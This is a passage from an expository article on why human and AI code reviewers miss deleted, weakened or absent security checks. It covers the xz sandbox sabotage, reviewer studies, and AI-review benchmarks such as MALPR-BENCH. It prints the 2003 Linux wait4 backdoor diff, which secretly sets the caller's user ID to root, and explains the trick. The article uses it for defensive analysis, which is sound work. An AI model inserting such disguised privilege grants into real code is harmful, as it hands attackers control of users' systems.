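Bantaloukas (2024), in *Sourceware mitigating and preventing the next xz-backdoor*, pointed out that failing to compile is an acceptable result for such a test, because that is how the test detects an unsupported system. The dot was also surrounded by pointless renames, and if anyone had noticed it, the contributor could have apologized for a typo.

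The dot was hard to see even for someone who knew that the commit disabled the sandbox. AlecTavi (2024), in *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure*, a comment on LWN, described reading the diff on a phone and then copying out the C program to look for a mistyped system call. The copy compiled because AlecTavi had removed the dot along with the plus signs, as if it were part of the diff's formatting.

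The maintainer Lasse Collin removed the dot on 30 March, about a month after the commit, with a one-line patch in *CMake* (Collin, 2024). In the patch's message, he wrote of the test, "It never enabled it." In a later review of Jia Tan's commits, published by Tukaani, he wrote that the dot "sabotages the Landlock detection". He also explained there that `xz` deliberately runs without a sandbox on kernels that don't support one, because otherwise it wouldn't run on those systems at all. Users therefore wouldn't have seen a missing sandbox as a fault.

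The sabotage probably affected few people. It was only in version 5.6.1, and only when built with CMake. sjw knew of no Linux distribution that built `xz` that way, and couldn't reproduce the problem with the more common build system.

In the builds the dot did affect, the sandbox could no longer block anything, so under the usual distinction this counts as a deleted check. But the reviewer had to catch it as they would a weakened one, by comparing two versions of a condition and working out which cases each would accept. A project can avoid relying on that comparison if one of its automated builds runs on a machine known to support Landlock and explicitly requires the sandbox. That build would have stopped with an error as soon as the dot was added.

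### The 2003 attempt on Linux

In November 2003 somebody added two lines to a copy of the Linux kernel's source code. McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, posted the difference to the kernel developers' mailing list:

```diff
+       if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
+               retval = -EINVAL;
        retval = -ECHILD;
```

The lines were in the function behind `wait4`, which a program uses to wait for another program it started. They look like a check that rejects an invalid combination of options. The first part of the condition tests for that combination. The second appears to test whether the user ID, `uid`, is 0, the ID of root, the administrator with full access to the system. The line below the `if` sets an error code for an invalid request.

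In C, however, `==` compares two values and a single `=` assigns one, so the code makes the user root instead of checking whether the user is root. C evaluates the second part of an `&&` condition only if the first part is true, so the assignment doesn't run during ordinary calls. Any program that calls `wait4` with the unusual combination of options gains complete control of the machine.

The apparent refusal, the line with the error code, never runs because the whole condition is false. An assignment in C also produces the value it assigned, in this case 0, which C treats as false. Even if the line did run, the next one would overwrite the result. One developer on the list also noticed that the parentheses around the assignment prevent a compiler warning.

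McVoy posted the lines as a comparison between files labelled GOOD and BAD, and still didn't notice the `=`. Within half an hour, another developer asked whether this was an attempt at a backdoor, and McVoy replied, "Good eyes, I missed that." Like AlecTavi, McVoy knew something was wrong with the code but overlooked the character that mattered.

The attempt failed because of how the lines were added. The official source code was in BitKeeper, and McVoy's company maintained a second copy for developers who preferred another system, CVS. According to Freedom to Tinker's *the linux backdoor attempt of 2003* (2013), someone had apparently broken into the CVS server and changed that copy directly. The company generated the CVS files on an internal machine before copying them to the public server, and every night it compared the checksums of the two sets. The altered file no longer matched. The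 change also lacked the usual pointer to an approved change in BitKeeper.

Linus Torvalds, who led the project, wrote on the mailing list that the lines could not have reached a kernel release, because the people who merged changes through BitKeeper didn't use the CVS copy and he or others would read any patch sent by email. McVoy was less certain and thought a CVS user could have unknowingly included the lines in a patch. Debian's *CVE-2003-1161* records that they never appeared in a release.

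The added lines resemble a check, but they are an insertion that grants a privilege, and the correct repair is to remove them. They don't fit any of the three forms, since `wait4` had no earlier version of this condition to loosen and wasn't missing a check it needed. They do enlarge the accept sets of other checks, because once a program is root, every check in the kernel that lets root through will also accept that program, but none of those checks appears in the diff.

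A reviewer of such a change can ask what the new check is for, even though there is no old condition to compare it with. One reader of Freedom to Tinker considered what the check would do if its author had meant to write `==`. It would have refused a harmless combination of options, and only when root requested it, which makes no sense as a rule.

An ordinary negative test might not have caught the backdoor. If it called `wait4` with the forbidden options and accepted any error as a refusal, it would have passed, because the line after the inserted code returns an error anyway. To catch the backdoor, the test would also have had to check the process's user ID after the call.

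## How human reviewers fare with missing and faulty checks

McVoy overlooked the stray `=` in the Linux backdoor even with the good and bad files side by side. People retell stories like this because something went wrong, so they don't show how often reviewers succeed. To get better evidence, some researchers search a project's history for flaws that reviewers caught or missed, and others plant flaws in code and ask developers to review it.

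### Catches and misses in Chromium OS

In *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021) studied past code reviews from Chromium OS, the open-source project behind the operating system of Google's Chromebooks. They compared 516 reviews in which a reviewer caught a security defect with 374 in which reviewers approved code containing one. This is a case-control study, a design that medical researchers use to compare people with and without a disease.

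The two groups contained very different kinds of defect. These are ten of the study's 15 categories:

| Kind of defect | Reviews that caught it | Reviews that missed it |
|---|---|---|
| Use of a dangerous function | 53 | 0 |
| Failure to release a resource properly | 71 | 4 |
| Improper synchronization | 109 | 13 |
| Incorrect calculation | 65 | 17 |
| Access outside a memory buffer | 42 | 16 |
| Poor handling of exceptional conditions | 58 | 22 |
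| Improper access control | 8 | 58 |
| Improper input validation | 9 | 72 |
| Use of a resource after its release | 3 | 62 |
| Insufficient verification of data authenticity | 0 | 13 |

Paul and colleagues collected the catches and the misses separately, so the share caught in the input-validation row, 9 in 81 or 11%, depends partly on how thoroughly they searched for each. That makes it unreliable as a detection rate, though they treat it as one when they write that these defects remained undetected in about 88% of reviews.

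To find security defects that reviewers had caught, the researchers searched 404,878 code review requests for comments containing any of 105 security keywords. They narrowed the 7,572 matching comments down by hand, keeping a review only if they agreed that the code was vulnerable and its author had acknowledged the problem or made the recommended change. To find defects that reviewers had missed, they started from 239 fixed security defects in the project's bug tracker and worked back to the changes that had introduced them.

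Suppose reviewers saw 100 input-validation defects and caught 50. If the keyword search turned up 10 of the catches and the bug tracker turned up 40 of the misses, the table would show 10 catches and 40 misses, and the detection rate would appear to be 20% instead of 50%.

Comparisons between categories are safer. The odds of a catch (catches divided by misses) are 65/17, or about 3.8, for incorrect calculations and 9/72, or about 0.13, for input validation. If the keyword search overlooked the same fraction of catches in every category, all the odds would be too low by the same factor, and the odds for incorrect calculations would still be about 31 times those for input validation.

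The search probably didn't find every type of defect equally well. Its keywords include "overflow", "race" and "permission" but not "validate", "sanitize" or "check", so it would have missed a comment like "please check that this is positive". But for this to explain the whole gap, the search would have had to find every caught calculation error and only about one in 31 of the caught input-validation defects. The bug tracker may also have been biased. The researchers took the categories of 124 missed defects from a public vulnerability database but assigned the rest themselves. Reviewers therefore probably did worse on input validation, but the study can't show by how much.

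It also can't show how the three forms compare. MITRE's categories for improper input validation and improper access control each include both missing and faulty checks. In the billing program, removing the `if` and `raise`, changing `and` to `or`, and adding the PDF route would all count as improper access control. An incorrect calculation might not involve a check at all.

The method for finding the misses makes the forms even harder to tell apart. The researchers' program started from each repair and used Git to find the change that had last touched the affected lines. A repair that adds a check has no old line to trace, so the program traced the lines just above and below the addition. That is reasonable if nobody ever wrote the check, but if a developer deleted it, the neighbouring lines might date from an earlier, harmless change. The researchers corrected the results by hand but don't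 report how many of the 374 changes deleted a check.

Paul and colleagues explain the pattern by how much code a reviewer has to understand. A call to a dangerous function is visible in one line, while access control and the lifetime of a resource depend on code further away. The table fits this explanation better than it fits a simple rule that reviewers miss omissions. Failing to release a resource is often an omission too, such as forgetting to close a file or free memory, yet reviewers caught 71 such defects and missed four. A reader who sees a file being opened expects to see it closed, but nothing in the PDF route would lead a reader to expect an ownership check unless they already knew `get_invoice`.

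The researchers also found that changes touching more directories were more likely to be among the misses. The odds of a catch were 4.55 times as high for bug fixes as for other changes, and also higher when the reviewer had often reviewed the same file. But reviewers who had taken part in more reviews overall did worse. The researchers suggest that fatigue, haste or a lack of specific security skills may explain this. These associations come from one project and from two groups with different origins, so they don't establish what caused the misses.

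### Two experiments with planted flaws

An experiment can measure a real detection rate because the researchers know that every reviewer's code contained the flaw. Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021), in *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, asked 146 people to review a Java change online. Of these, 105 had at least three years of professional programming experience. The change was about 140 lines long and added a feature for managing employees' vacations.

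The researchers randomly assigned each person one of two versions of the program. One version pasted an employee's ID straight into a database query, which allowed SQL injection. The other accepted a whole number without checking its range, so a negative number gave the user an unintended benefit. For example, if a program subtracts the requested days from an employee's balance, a request for −5 days adds five.

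The participants didn't know the study was about security. After the participants' first review, the researchers told them the code contained a vulnerability, but not what kind, and let those who had missed it look again.

| Planted flaw | Reviewers | Found in first review | Found after the warning | Never found |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | 80 | 52 | 13 | 15 |
| Unchecked quantity | 66 | 14 | 7 | 45 |

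In the first review, 65% found the SQL injection and 21% found the unchecked quantity. With the warning, the totals rose to 81% and 32%. (The figures for the unchecked quantity come from the paper's tables; its text gives 18% and 40%.) Developers were about three times as likely to detect the SQL injection as the unchecked quantity in the first review. Braz and colleagues say seven times, but that figure is a ratio of odds (52/28 against 14/52).

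Carelessness alone doesn't explain why reviewers missed the unchecked quantity. The researchers had also planted an ordinary bug, a mishandled corner case, to see whether people were making an effort. In the group with the unchecked quantity, 37 of 66 reviewers found that bug, but only about a fifth found the missing range check. In the other group, 39 of 80 found the ordinary bug.

Both planted flaws are closest to never-written checks, because a new feature lacked the validation it needed. The unchecked quantity is the clearer example, because developers usually fix SQL injection by passing the value to the database separately from the query, which doesn't reject any input.

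The changed lines contained everything a reviewer needed to find either flaw. For the PDF route, a reviewer may also have to find `get_invoice` in another file, so the detection rate could be lower than 21%. But people who review their own project's code know its rules and have more at stake than volunteers in an online study.

Of the 52 people who had missed the unchecked quantity, 45 still couldn't find it after the warning that something was wrong. Some said they had mistaken the corner-case bug for the vulnerability, and others said they lacked the knowledge or experience. The experiment can't show how much of the improvement came from the warning, because no group looked at the code a second time without one.

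*Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) addressed that problem by giving separate groups different instructions before a single review. The 150 participants reviewed a 160-line Java change that registered users for a web service and contained two flaws. When a database query failed, the program wrote the query to an error log, including the user's email address and unencrypted password. It also protected stored passwords with MD5, an outdated algorithm that attackers can break quickly.

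One group received no security instructions, and the researchers asked the other three to focus on security. Two of those three also had to work through a checklist. One checklist had 22 questions adapted from OWASP's code review guide, and the other had only the seven relevant to the change. Both checklists contained questions that pointed to the planted flaws.

| Instructions | Reviewers | Found the password in the log | Found MD5 |
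|---|---|---|---|
| None about security | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Focus on security | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| Focus on security, with 22 questions | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| Focus on security, with 7 questions | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

Of the 33 reviewers without security instructions, 8 (24%) found at least one flaw. Of the 117 in the other three groups, 84 (72%) did. The probability of detection was therefore three times as high, and the odds were about eight times as high (84/33 against 8/25). The paper's abstract says that asking for a security focus increased the probability of detection eight times, but here too the figure is a ratio of odds.

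The checklists made no statistically significant difference. With about 40 people in each group, the study could have missed a modest benefit, but it found no sign of a large one. Some participants read the checklist only after finishing their review. Others read the relevant question but didn't know enough to answer it, including one who had judged MD5 a good choice. Of the 76 people who had a checklist, 32 found it helpful.

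These flaws belong to none of the three forms. Each is a visible line that exposes a password or names a weak algorithm, and fixing it doesn't involve refusing a request. They therefore give no good reason to expect an eightfold improvement for missing checks. In the 2021 experiment, the warning raised the odds of finding the unchecked quantity from 14/52 to 21/45, a factor of about 1.7. The two studies have different designs, so the comparison is rough, but it suggests that telling reviewers to look for security problems helps less when the problem is a missing check.

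### Why an absence may be harder to notice

One possible explanation from psychology is the feature-positive effect, a tendency to learn more easily from something present than from something absent. Jenkins and Sainsbury described it around 1970 in experiments with pigeons. The birds saw two displays that were identical except for an extra mark on one of them, and pecking at only one of the displays earned food. The pigeons learned to tell the displays apart when the mark was on the rewarded one, but mostly kept pecking at both when it was on the other. In 1980 Newman, Wolff and Hearst reported a similar effect in adults, who had to work out what made some sets of symbols "good". The adults found the rule more easily when it depended on the presence of a symbol than on its absence.

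If the effect carries over to code review, reviewers should notice a deleted check more readily than a never-written one, because the diff shows the removed lines. But the pigeons and the adults were learning an unknown rule from repeated feedback. Reviewers usually wait months for feedback, if they get any, and may already know the rule from comparable code such as `get_invoice`. None of the code review studies discussed here tests the effect.

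The 2021 experiment comes closest, because both versions lacked validation but one also contained a conspicuous cue. A database query assembled from pieces of text is a well-known warning sign, so a reviewer who recognizes it can find the flaw without thinking of the missing validation. The other version had no such cue, because an unchecked number looks like any other number. The results fit both the feature-positive effect and a simpler explanation, familiarity. Participants who found the SQL injection often said it was a common flaw or that they had seen it before. The experiment changed the visible cue and the familiarity of the attack together, so it can't separate their effects.

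No experiment discussed here compares deleted, never-written and weakened checks, and neither of the two by Braz and colleagues included a deleted or weakened one. The expectation that reviewers catch deleted checks most easily therefore rests on what the diff shows them and on individual cases. Not all of those cases support it, since the stray dot in `xz` amounted to a deletion but was easy to overlook. Researchers could test the expectation directly and fairly simply by giving each reviewer the billing program with one of the three changes and counting how many people in each group object.

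### Reviewing code written by an AI system

Reviewers may also behave differently when they believe that an AI system wrote the code. In *Same Scrutiny, More Time*, Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues (2026) tracked the eye movements of 32 software practitioners from 20 organizations while they reviewed four short Python files. Labels attributed some sections to a fictional AI assistant, CodeForgeAI, but people had written all the code. The same section appeared with the label for some participants and without it for others, so any difference in behaviour came from the label, not the quality of the code.

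Participants looked at labelled sections for longer. On a complicated section of 25 lines, the label added about 15 seconds, or 60%. On very short sections it made little difference. The label didn't change how far participants' eyes jumped between resting points, which indicates whether they were reading closely, line by line (short jumps), or skimming (long jumps). Participants who said they read AI-generated code more thoroughly spent more time on it but scanned it the same way.

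The researchers planted some faults to make the task realistic but didn't score how many each person found, so whether the extra time helped reviewers find faults is unknown. The label also included coloured highlighting and the prompt that had supposedly produced the code, so some of the added attention may have been a response to these rather than to the idea of an AI author.

For never-written checks, the prompt may matter more than the label. Fourteen of the 32 participants said they used the prompt in their review. Seven treated it as a description of the code's purpose, five as a requirement to compare the code with, and two as both. Comparing code with a prompt is a good way to find a feature the assistant forgot, but it can't reveal a missing check that the prompt never mentioned. If a developer asked for "a PDF download for invoices", the unprotected PDF route does what the prompt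 requested. One participant described glancing at the code for anything "absolutely stupid" and otherwise relying on the tests, which would also miss the open route if they covered only normal use.

These participants at least had to read the code. Guo and colleagues cite a 2025 paper by Li, Zhang and Hassan for the finding that 58.2% of agent-written pull requests in popular GitHub repositories received no explicit review. Some of those pull requests may have been closed or left open rather than merged, and developers may have read others and merged them without leaving a formal review on GitHub. Guo and colleagues also cite GitHub's own figures, in which the share of pull requests that began as an agent's draft rose from 17% in March 2026 to more than 40% in September.

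*Security in the Age of AI Teammates* (Siddiq, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) examined how projects treated 33,596 agent-written pull requests from late 2024 to the third quarter of 2025. It identified 1,293 as security-related, meaning that their main purpose was to prevent or fix a security problem. Projects merged 61.5% of the security-related pull requests they closed, compared with 77.3% of the others. The median time from opening to closing was 3.92 hours for security-related pull requests and about seven minutes for the rest.

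Siddiq and colleagues interpret this as heightened scrutiny of security work, but much of the difference in merge rates comes from the mix of agents. OpenAI's Codex wrote almost two thirds of all the pull requests and had the highest merge rate, but only 1.3% of its pull requests were security-related. Within each agent, the gap is mostly smaller:

| Agent | Security-related pull requests merged | Others merged |
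|---|---|---|
| Codex | 86.6% | 85.8% |
| Cursor | 76.5% | 74.5% |
| Claude Code | 58.6% | 73.6% |
| Devin | 52.1% | 55.8% |
| Copilot | 49.6% | 55.5% |

If the other pull requests had come from the five agents in the same proportions as the security-related ones, their merge rate would have been about 64% instead of 77%, leaving a gap of about three percentage points between the two groups. The seven-minute median also needs caution, because a single repository supplied 8,913 of the pull requests, more than a quarter. Time is also a weak measure of attention, because a pull request can wait unopened for hours, and a developer may have read the code before the agent submitted it.

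Even if security-related pull requests receive more attention, a pull request with a missing check may not be counted as one. The researchers found security-related pull requests by searching titles and descriptions for words such as "security", "authentication" and "vulnerability", and confirmed the results by hand. A pull request called "Add PDF download for invoices" contains none of these words, so it would have been counted among the non-security pull requests, which had a median of seven minutes.

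## How AI reviewers and static analysers fare with each form

An automated reviewer can read every pull request, including those that people merge within minutes. It usually gives a verdict, such as approve or block, and explains it in comments. The verdict can be right even when the explanation is wrong. Suppose a tool blocks the PDF route because of how the code builds the file name. The author rewrites that line and the tool approves the change, but all 1,000 users can still download invoice 17.

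### What MALPR-BENCH measures

Chen and colleagues designed MALPR-BENCH to score the verdict and the explanation separately. Before grading any reviews, they wrote a rubric for each of the 89 malicious pull requests. It names the flaw that makes the change unsafe, the descriptions they would accept, the facts a review has to establish, and nearby problems that earn no credit. Each review then gets three yes-or-no scores:

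- Blocking: the reviewer refuses the change.
- Naming: the review describes the affected behaviour, the missing or broken condition, and the consequence. "Authorization issue" is too vague to count.
- Evidence: the review names the flaw and also cites the code that proves it.

For the PDF route, a review would earn the naming score by explaining that any logged-in user can download any invoice because the code never checks whether the user owns it. To earn the evidence score, it would also have to cite the unguarded lookup and something that shows a guard is needed, such as `get_invoice`. Two language models graded naming and evidence without being told which tool wrote each review. Two people together settled the cases where the models' grades differed and checked some of the cases where they matched.

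The malicious pull requests come from five groups:

| Group | Malicious | Safe controls | Where the cases come from |
|---|---|---|---|
| Development | 14 | 0 | Incomplete fixes in project histories, used to build the researchers' own reviewer |
| History | 19 | 6 | Incomplete fixes in the histories of other projects |
| Reversed fixes | 37 | 37 | Security fixes from 2025, with a protective change undone |
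| Omissions | 7 | 7 | Security fixes from 2025, with one protective change left out |
| Discoveries | 12 | 0 | New vulnerabilities that the researchers' reviewer found |

Each control contains the complete fix for one of the malicious cases, so a tool that blocks it has raised a false alarm.

The researchers ran their reviewer, PRGuard, with two language models, OpenAI's GPT-5.5 and the open-weight DeepSeek v4-pro. An ordinary program first collects code related to the change, including callers, called functions and similar functions that might need the same guard. The model then describes what changed, without yet proposing flaws. PRGuard retrieves more code, guided partly by 21 flaw patterns that the researchers derived from the development cases, and the model proposes flaws. In a separate step, the model tests each proposed flaw against the code. PRGuard blocks the change if the code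 supports every part of at least one proposal. If the best proposal still has a gap, PRGuard only comments.

### Protection removed in view and protection left out

The reversed fixes and the omissions give the most direct comparison between removing protection and failing to add it.

| Result | Reversed fixes (37) | Omissions (7) |
|---|---|---|
| Flaw named, GPT-5.5 | 37 | 3 |
| Flaw named, DeepSeek | 37 | 3 |
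| Flaw named with evidence, GPT-5.5 | 26 | 3 |
| Flaw named with evidence, DeepSeek | 34 | 2 |
| Change blocked, GPT-5.5 | 26 | 4 |
| Change blocked, DeepSeek | 33 | 4 |

Both versions identified the flaw in every reversed fix. But the GPT-5.5 version blocked only 26 of the 37, so for the other 11 a maintainer would have had to read the comments to learn of the problem. Among the omissions, each version blocked four changes but identified the flaw in only three, so each blocked at least one for the wrong reason.

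One omission comes from memos, a note-taking program. The real fix involved protection at six places in the code. Chen and colleagues left out the attachment check that refuses a user who didn't create the memo. A reviewer would see much of a sensible repair and have to notice that this check was missing.

The gap is unlikely to be due to chance. If the reviewer were equally likely to miss a flaw in either group, all four misses would fall among the seven omissions only about once in 3,900 times. The detection rate for omissions is still very uncertain. The reviewer caught three of the seven, which gives a 95% confidence interval of about 10% to 82%.

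The two groups also differ in where a reviewer has to look. In all seven omissions, the missing protection belonged outside the changed lines, and in two of them it belonged in a file the pull request didn't touch. The comparison therefore can't separate the difficulty of noticing that something is missing from the difficulty of looking beyond the diff.

The reversed fixes were probably easier to catch than many real deletions. Chen and colleagues narrowed 3,688 security advisories to 237 about authorization in web software. Only 50 of these had a guard that could be undone in a single place, and 37 passed a manual check. This group would not include a guard that is lost in a large rewrite, as OpenSSH's was.

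These 37 cases also don't give separate rates for deleted and weakened checks. Undoing a fix deletes a check if the fix added a whole one, or weakens it if the fix tightened a condition. Chen and colleagues describe the seven omissions one by one in their appendices but don't do the same for the reversed fixes, so the two kinds can't be counted. Each fix had to contain a guard that could be undone in one place, which suggests that many of the reversals were deletions.

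PRGuard's verdicts were less stable than its explanations. When the researchers reran it on these 44 pull requests, the GPT-5.5 version changed its verdict on eight and the DeepSeek version on 11, while the score for naming the flaw changed in only two and three cases respectively. *SEVRA-BENCH* (Melo, Fogliato and colleagues, 2026) found that misleading descriptions can also make AI reviewers less likely to reject reversed fixes.

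### Reviewing the diff alone

Chen and colleagues tested how much the surrounding code helps by running both versions of PRGuard with only the diff on 12 absence-type cases, made up of the seven omissions and five cases from the history group. The GPT-5.5 version blocked one, for an unrelated reason, and the DeepSeek version blocked none. With the full system, the GPT-5.5 version blocked six and the DeepSeek version blocked five.

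The full system blocked five cases that the diff-only version did not, and the reverse never happened. If the full system made no difference, all five changes would be toward blocking about one time in 32. Not all of the additional blocks were for the right reason, since each version made at least one mistaken block among the omissions. The full system also differs from the diff-only version in several ways, so the experiment doesn't show which part helped.

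The diff was more useful in the history group as a whole, where 14 of the 19 flaws are present-type. From the diff alone, the GPT-5.5 version named 13 flaws and the DeepSeek version 10. The full system raised these figures only to 14 and 12. The additional code raised the evidence score more, from 6 to 12 for one version and from 6 to 10 for the other. When the diff contains the faulty behaviour, a model can often name the likely flaw from the diff alone and needs the rest of the repository mainly to prove it.

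### A commercial reviewer and the distance to the evidence

Chen and colleagues also tested CodeRabbit, a commercial AI reviewer with more than 300,000 installations on GitHub's marketplace. Because of its cost and usage limits, they ran it only on the 31 cases in the history and discovery groups. The table compares CodeRabbit with the DeepSeek version of PRGuard.

| Reviewer | Present-type: blocked | Present-type: named | Absence-type: blocked | Absence-type: named |
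|---|---|---|---|---|
| CodeRabbit | 15 of 17 | 13 of 17 | 9 of 14 | 3 of 14 |
| PRGuard with DeepSeek | 13 of 17 | 13 of 17 | 9 of 14 | 9 of 14 |

In at least six of the nine missing-check cases that CodeRabbit blocked, it objected to something other than the missing check. For example, when a client could resume another project's run, CodeRabbit objected to how the client displayed secrets. The developers could have fixed the display and left the runs exposed. A benchmark that counted only blocks would still rate the two tools as equal on missing checks.

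*Beyond True or False* (2026), which separately tested whether language models can explain vulnerabilities, found a similar problem. Of the 2,394 correct verdicts, 725 (30.3%) rested on incorrect reasoning.

#### Four levels of evidence

CodeRabbit also did worse when the evidence was farther from the diff. On MALPR-BENCH's scale, L0 and L1 cases need evidence only from the files that the pull request changes. L2a and L2b cases need evidence from other files, and at L2b those files are related to the change only because they do a similar job. A case that needs evidence from several places gets the label for the most distant one. CodeRabbit named the flaw in 16 of the 24 cases at L0 or L1, but in none of the seven at L2a or L2b.

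Six of those seven distant cases are also absence-type, so distance and absence are mixed together here too. The case lists and totals that Chen and colleagues give are detailed enough to separate them for CodeRabbit:

| Flaws CodeRabbit named | Evidence in the changed files | Evidence in other files |
|---|---|---|
| Present-type | 13 of 16 | 0 of 1 |
| Absence-type | 3 of 8 | 0 of 6 |

CodeRabbit did worse on absences even when all the evidence was in the changed files. A gap at least that large in that direction would arise by chance about one time in 20, so this evidence is suggestive but not strong. The table has only one distant present-type case, so it can't show whether distance alone would have the same effect.

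#### Access to the whole repository

A tool that can search every file should in principle be able to find evidence far from the changed code. Chen and colleagues tested this with OpenAI's Codex, giving it the diff and the full repository without saying what to look for. Codex reviewed each of seven malicious pull requests twice.

Codex reviewed each of the seven cases twice. On the four L1 cases, it blocked the change in six of eight runs and named the flaw in three of the four cases. On the three L2b cases, it blocked the change in four of six runs but never named the flaw. One of these three was the unguarded device-code flow in authentik, which Codex approved in one run and blocked for the wrong reason in the other.

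Codex did search, making between 12 and 47 tool calls and reading between 5 and 23 files per review across these reviews and those of six harmless changes. It seems to have had trouble working out which unchanged function to compare with the new one. The seven cases were deliberately chosen, so they can show that this happens but not how often.

#### How far to trust the comparison

PRGuard's lead over CodeRabbit comes entirely from the 12 vulnerabilities that PRGuard itself had originally found. On those, the DeepSeek version of PRGuard named ten flaws and CodeRabbit named four. On the other 19 cases, each tool named 12 flaws, but CodeRabbit did slightly better at the complete task of blocking the change, naming the flaw and supplying the evidence, succeeding in 12 cases to PRGuard's nine.

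Chen and colleagues acknowledge that the selection favours the GPT-5.5 version, which found the vulnerabilities, so they leave its score out of the main comparison. But the DeepSeek version uses the same flaw patterns and the same program to collect code, so it probably benefits as well. PRGuard discovered nine of the 14 absence-type cases. The reported totals imply that the DeepSeek version blocked eight of those nine and only one of the other five. PRGuard's threefold lead on absent checks is therefore weak evidence of how the tools would compare on a new set of pull requests.

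The case selection is less of a problem for CodeRabbit's results. The researchers didn't choose any case because CodeRabbit had failed on it, and the tool still named a smaller share of the absent checks (3 of 14) than of the present-type flaws (13 of 17).

False alarms don't seem to explain the results, though the control samples were small. The GPT-5.5 version of PRGuard blocked five of the 50 safe controls, and the DeepSeek version blocked four. CodeRabbit reviewed only six controls and blocked none.

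### Static analysers

A static analyser examines code without running it, usually by applying fixed rules. A common type of rule traces data from an untrusted source, such as a web request, to a dangerous operation, such as a database query built from text. Chen and colleagues ran CodeQL, GitHub's analyser, with its standard extended set of security rules. The rules applied to 21 of the 31 cases that CodeRabbit had reviewed. CodeQL identified none of the flaws, and its only blocking alert was about a different issue.

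A general rule of this kind doesn't specify who may read an invoice. In the PDF route, a number from the web address reaches `invoices.find`, but the same happens in `get_invoice` and in any ordinary page that displays a record. Changing `and` to `or` doesn't change the data's path. A project's developers could write a rule requiring every route that returns an invoice to call an approved ownership check, and the PDF route would fail it. The test of CodeQL covered only the standard rules, so it doesn't show how well such a rule would work.

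Rules are better suited to flaws in how a program handles memory, since some operations are unsafe whatever the project's policy, but the results are still modest. *SBVUL* (Pinzger, Stengg and colleagues, 2026) cites an earlier comparison of five analysers on 112 memory-safety bugs in C and C++ programs. CodeQL found the most, 31 (28%). Only 0.24% of its reports matched a known bug, so somebody would have had to read more than 400 reports for each match. Some of the unmatched reports may have been about real bugs that nobody had recorded.

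No analyser in these tests looked specifically for checks that were in the old version of the code but missing from the new one. A project that wants automatic warnings about deleted checks needs a tool that compares the two versions, such as one that lists removed conditions. Such a list would have included OpenSSH's guard.

### Weakened checks and paired tests

MALPR-BENCH doesn't score weakened checks separately, so the closest evidence comes from paired tests. These give a language model a vulnerable function and its repaired version separately, and the model gets credit only if it flags the first and clears the second. For `get_invoice`, it would have to flag the version with `or` and clear the one with `and`. A model that flags any function dealing with private records would flag both versions and get no credit.

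Cichoń and Dmitruk (2026), in *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model*, gave six sets of such pairs to seven models. The models judged between 6% and 25% of the pairs correctly. On the largest set, with 1,000 pairs of C and C++ functions, three of the better-known models gave these results:

| Model | Both correct | Flagged both | Cleared both | Both wrong |
|---|---|---|---|---|
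| Grok 4.3 | 25.4% | 53.0% | 17.9% | 3.7% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 17.7% | 53.3% | 27.1% | 1.9% |
| GPT-5.2 | 11.1% | 81.9% | 5.1% | 1.9% |

A coin toss for each function would also judge 25% of the pairs correctly and get another 25% backwards. Cichoń and Dmitruk therefore subtract the backwards pairs from the correct ones. This gives the coin toss a score of zero, Grok 4.3 a score of 21.7 points and GPT-5.2 a score of 9.2. These models respond to the repair, but only in a small share of pairs.

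The researchers also tested 61 open models, most of them much smaller. Of all 68 models, 37 had scores indistinguishable from zero. Cichoń and Dmitruk conclude that the verdict depends on the text the two versions share, which in `get_invoice` is everything except one word.

#### How much these pairs resemble a loosened condition

The repaired function is longer in 87.5% of the 1,000 pairs, so most repairs added code. Many of the vulnerable versions probably lacked a check altogether, and the researchers didn't select pairs that differ by a single condition. They also showed each function without its callers or the rest of the project, and some functions can't be judged without that context.

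Another of their experiments is more relevant to loosened conditions. The researchers trained linear probes, which are simple classifiers, on the numbers that open models compute internally while reading a function. On pairs of nearly equal length, the typical probe picked out the vulnerable version 78% of the time. The six models they compared in this way did so only 50% to 57% of the time in their written verdicts. The models' internal state therefore contained information about the flaw that their answers didn't reflect.

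However, on the 125 pairs in which the repair made the function shorter, the typical probe was right only 55% of the time, close to chance. It seems to have learned to recognize the code that repairs usually add. A repair that changes `or` back to `and` adds almost nothing, so the probe may not help much with a weakened check.

*TREAT* (2025) similarly reports that even the best models struggled to distinguish vulnerable functions from repaired ones when the differences were subtle and the code contained few visible cues. Most ways of loosening a condition fit that description, though *TREAT* doesn't isolate them either.

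A model may also accept a guard too readily. *Neuro-Symbolic Reasoning for Vulnerability Detection* (2026) attributes unreliable detection mainly to "premature discharge", in which a model treats a safety requirement as met before anything has established this. A model could easily make this mistake with the `or` version of `get_invoice`, because it contains an ownership test, a condition and a refusal. In the proposed remedy, LeanGuard, a language model supplies facts about the code and a theorem prover checks whether each guard covers the operation it should protect. With LeanGuard, the share of double frees found, in which a program releases the same memory twice, rose from 21% to 41%. The same approach might help with loosened conditions, but someone would still have to state the billing policy for the prover to check.

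#### Newer models with access to the repository

Pinzger and colleagues gave a newer model, Claude Opus 5.5, 200 pairs and let it search each project's code. One agent listed suspicious statements in the function, and another looked for evidence that each was exploitable. The model judged 84 of the pairs (42%) correctly. For 73 of those, it had also confirmed an exploitable statement and explained it correctly.

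That is clearly better than the 9% that Claude Opus 4.8 achieved in Cichoń and Dmitruk's tests on pairs from the same collection, PrimeVul. The studies differ in the model, the instructions, the access to other files and the pairs used, so the gain can't be attributed to any one of these.

False alarms remained the main problem. Claude Opus 5.5 flagged 94% of the vulnerable functions but also 54% of the repaired ones. A developer who fixed a weakened condition in response to a warning would often get another warning about the corrected code.

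At its highest effort setting, the model confirmed the flaw in 84% of the functions that read or wrote outside a memory buffer, eight of the 16 with an improper check or poor handling of exceptional conditions, and five of the seven with access-control or authentication flaws. The last two groups are small, and neither separates missing checks from weak ones.

Pinzger and colleagues report that 58 of the 200 repairs only inserted code, typically a check before an unchanged operation. Those vulnerable functions resemble never-written or deleted checks more than weakened ones. The researchers also replaced four pairs because the flaw was a missing statement whose effect appeared only in other functions, so their results exclude some flaws of omission.

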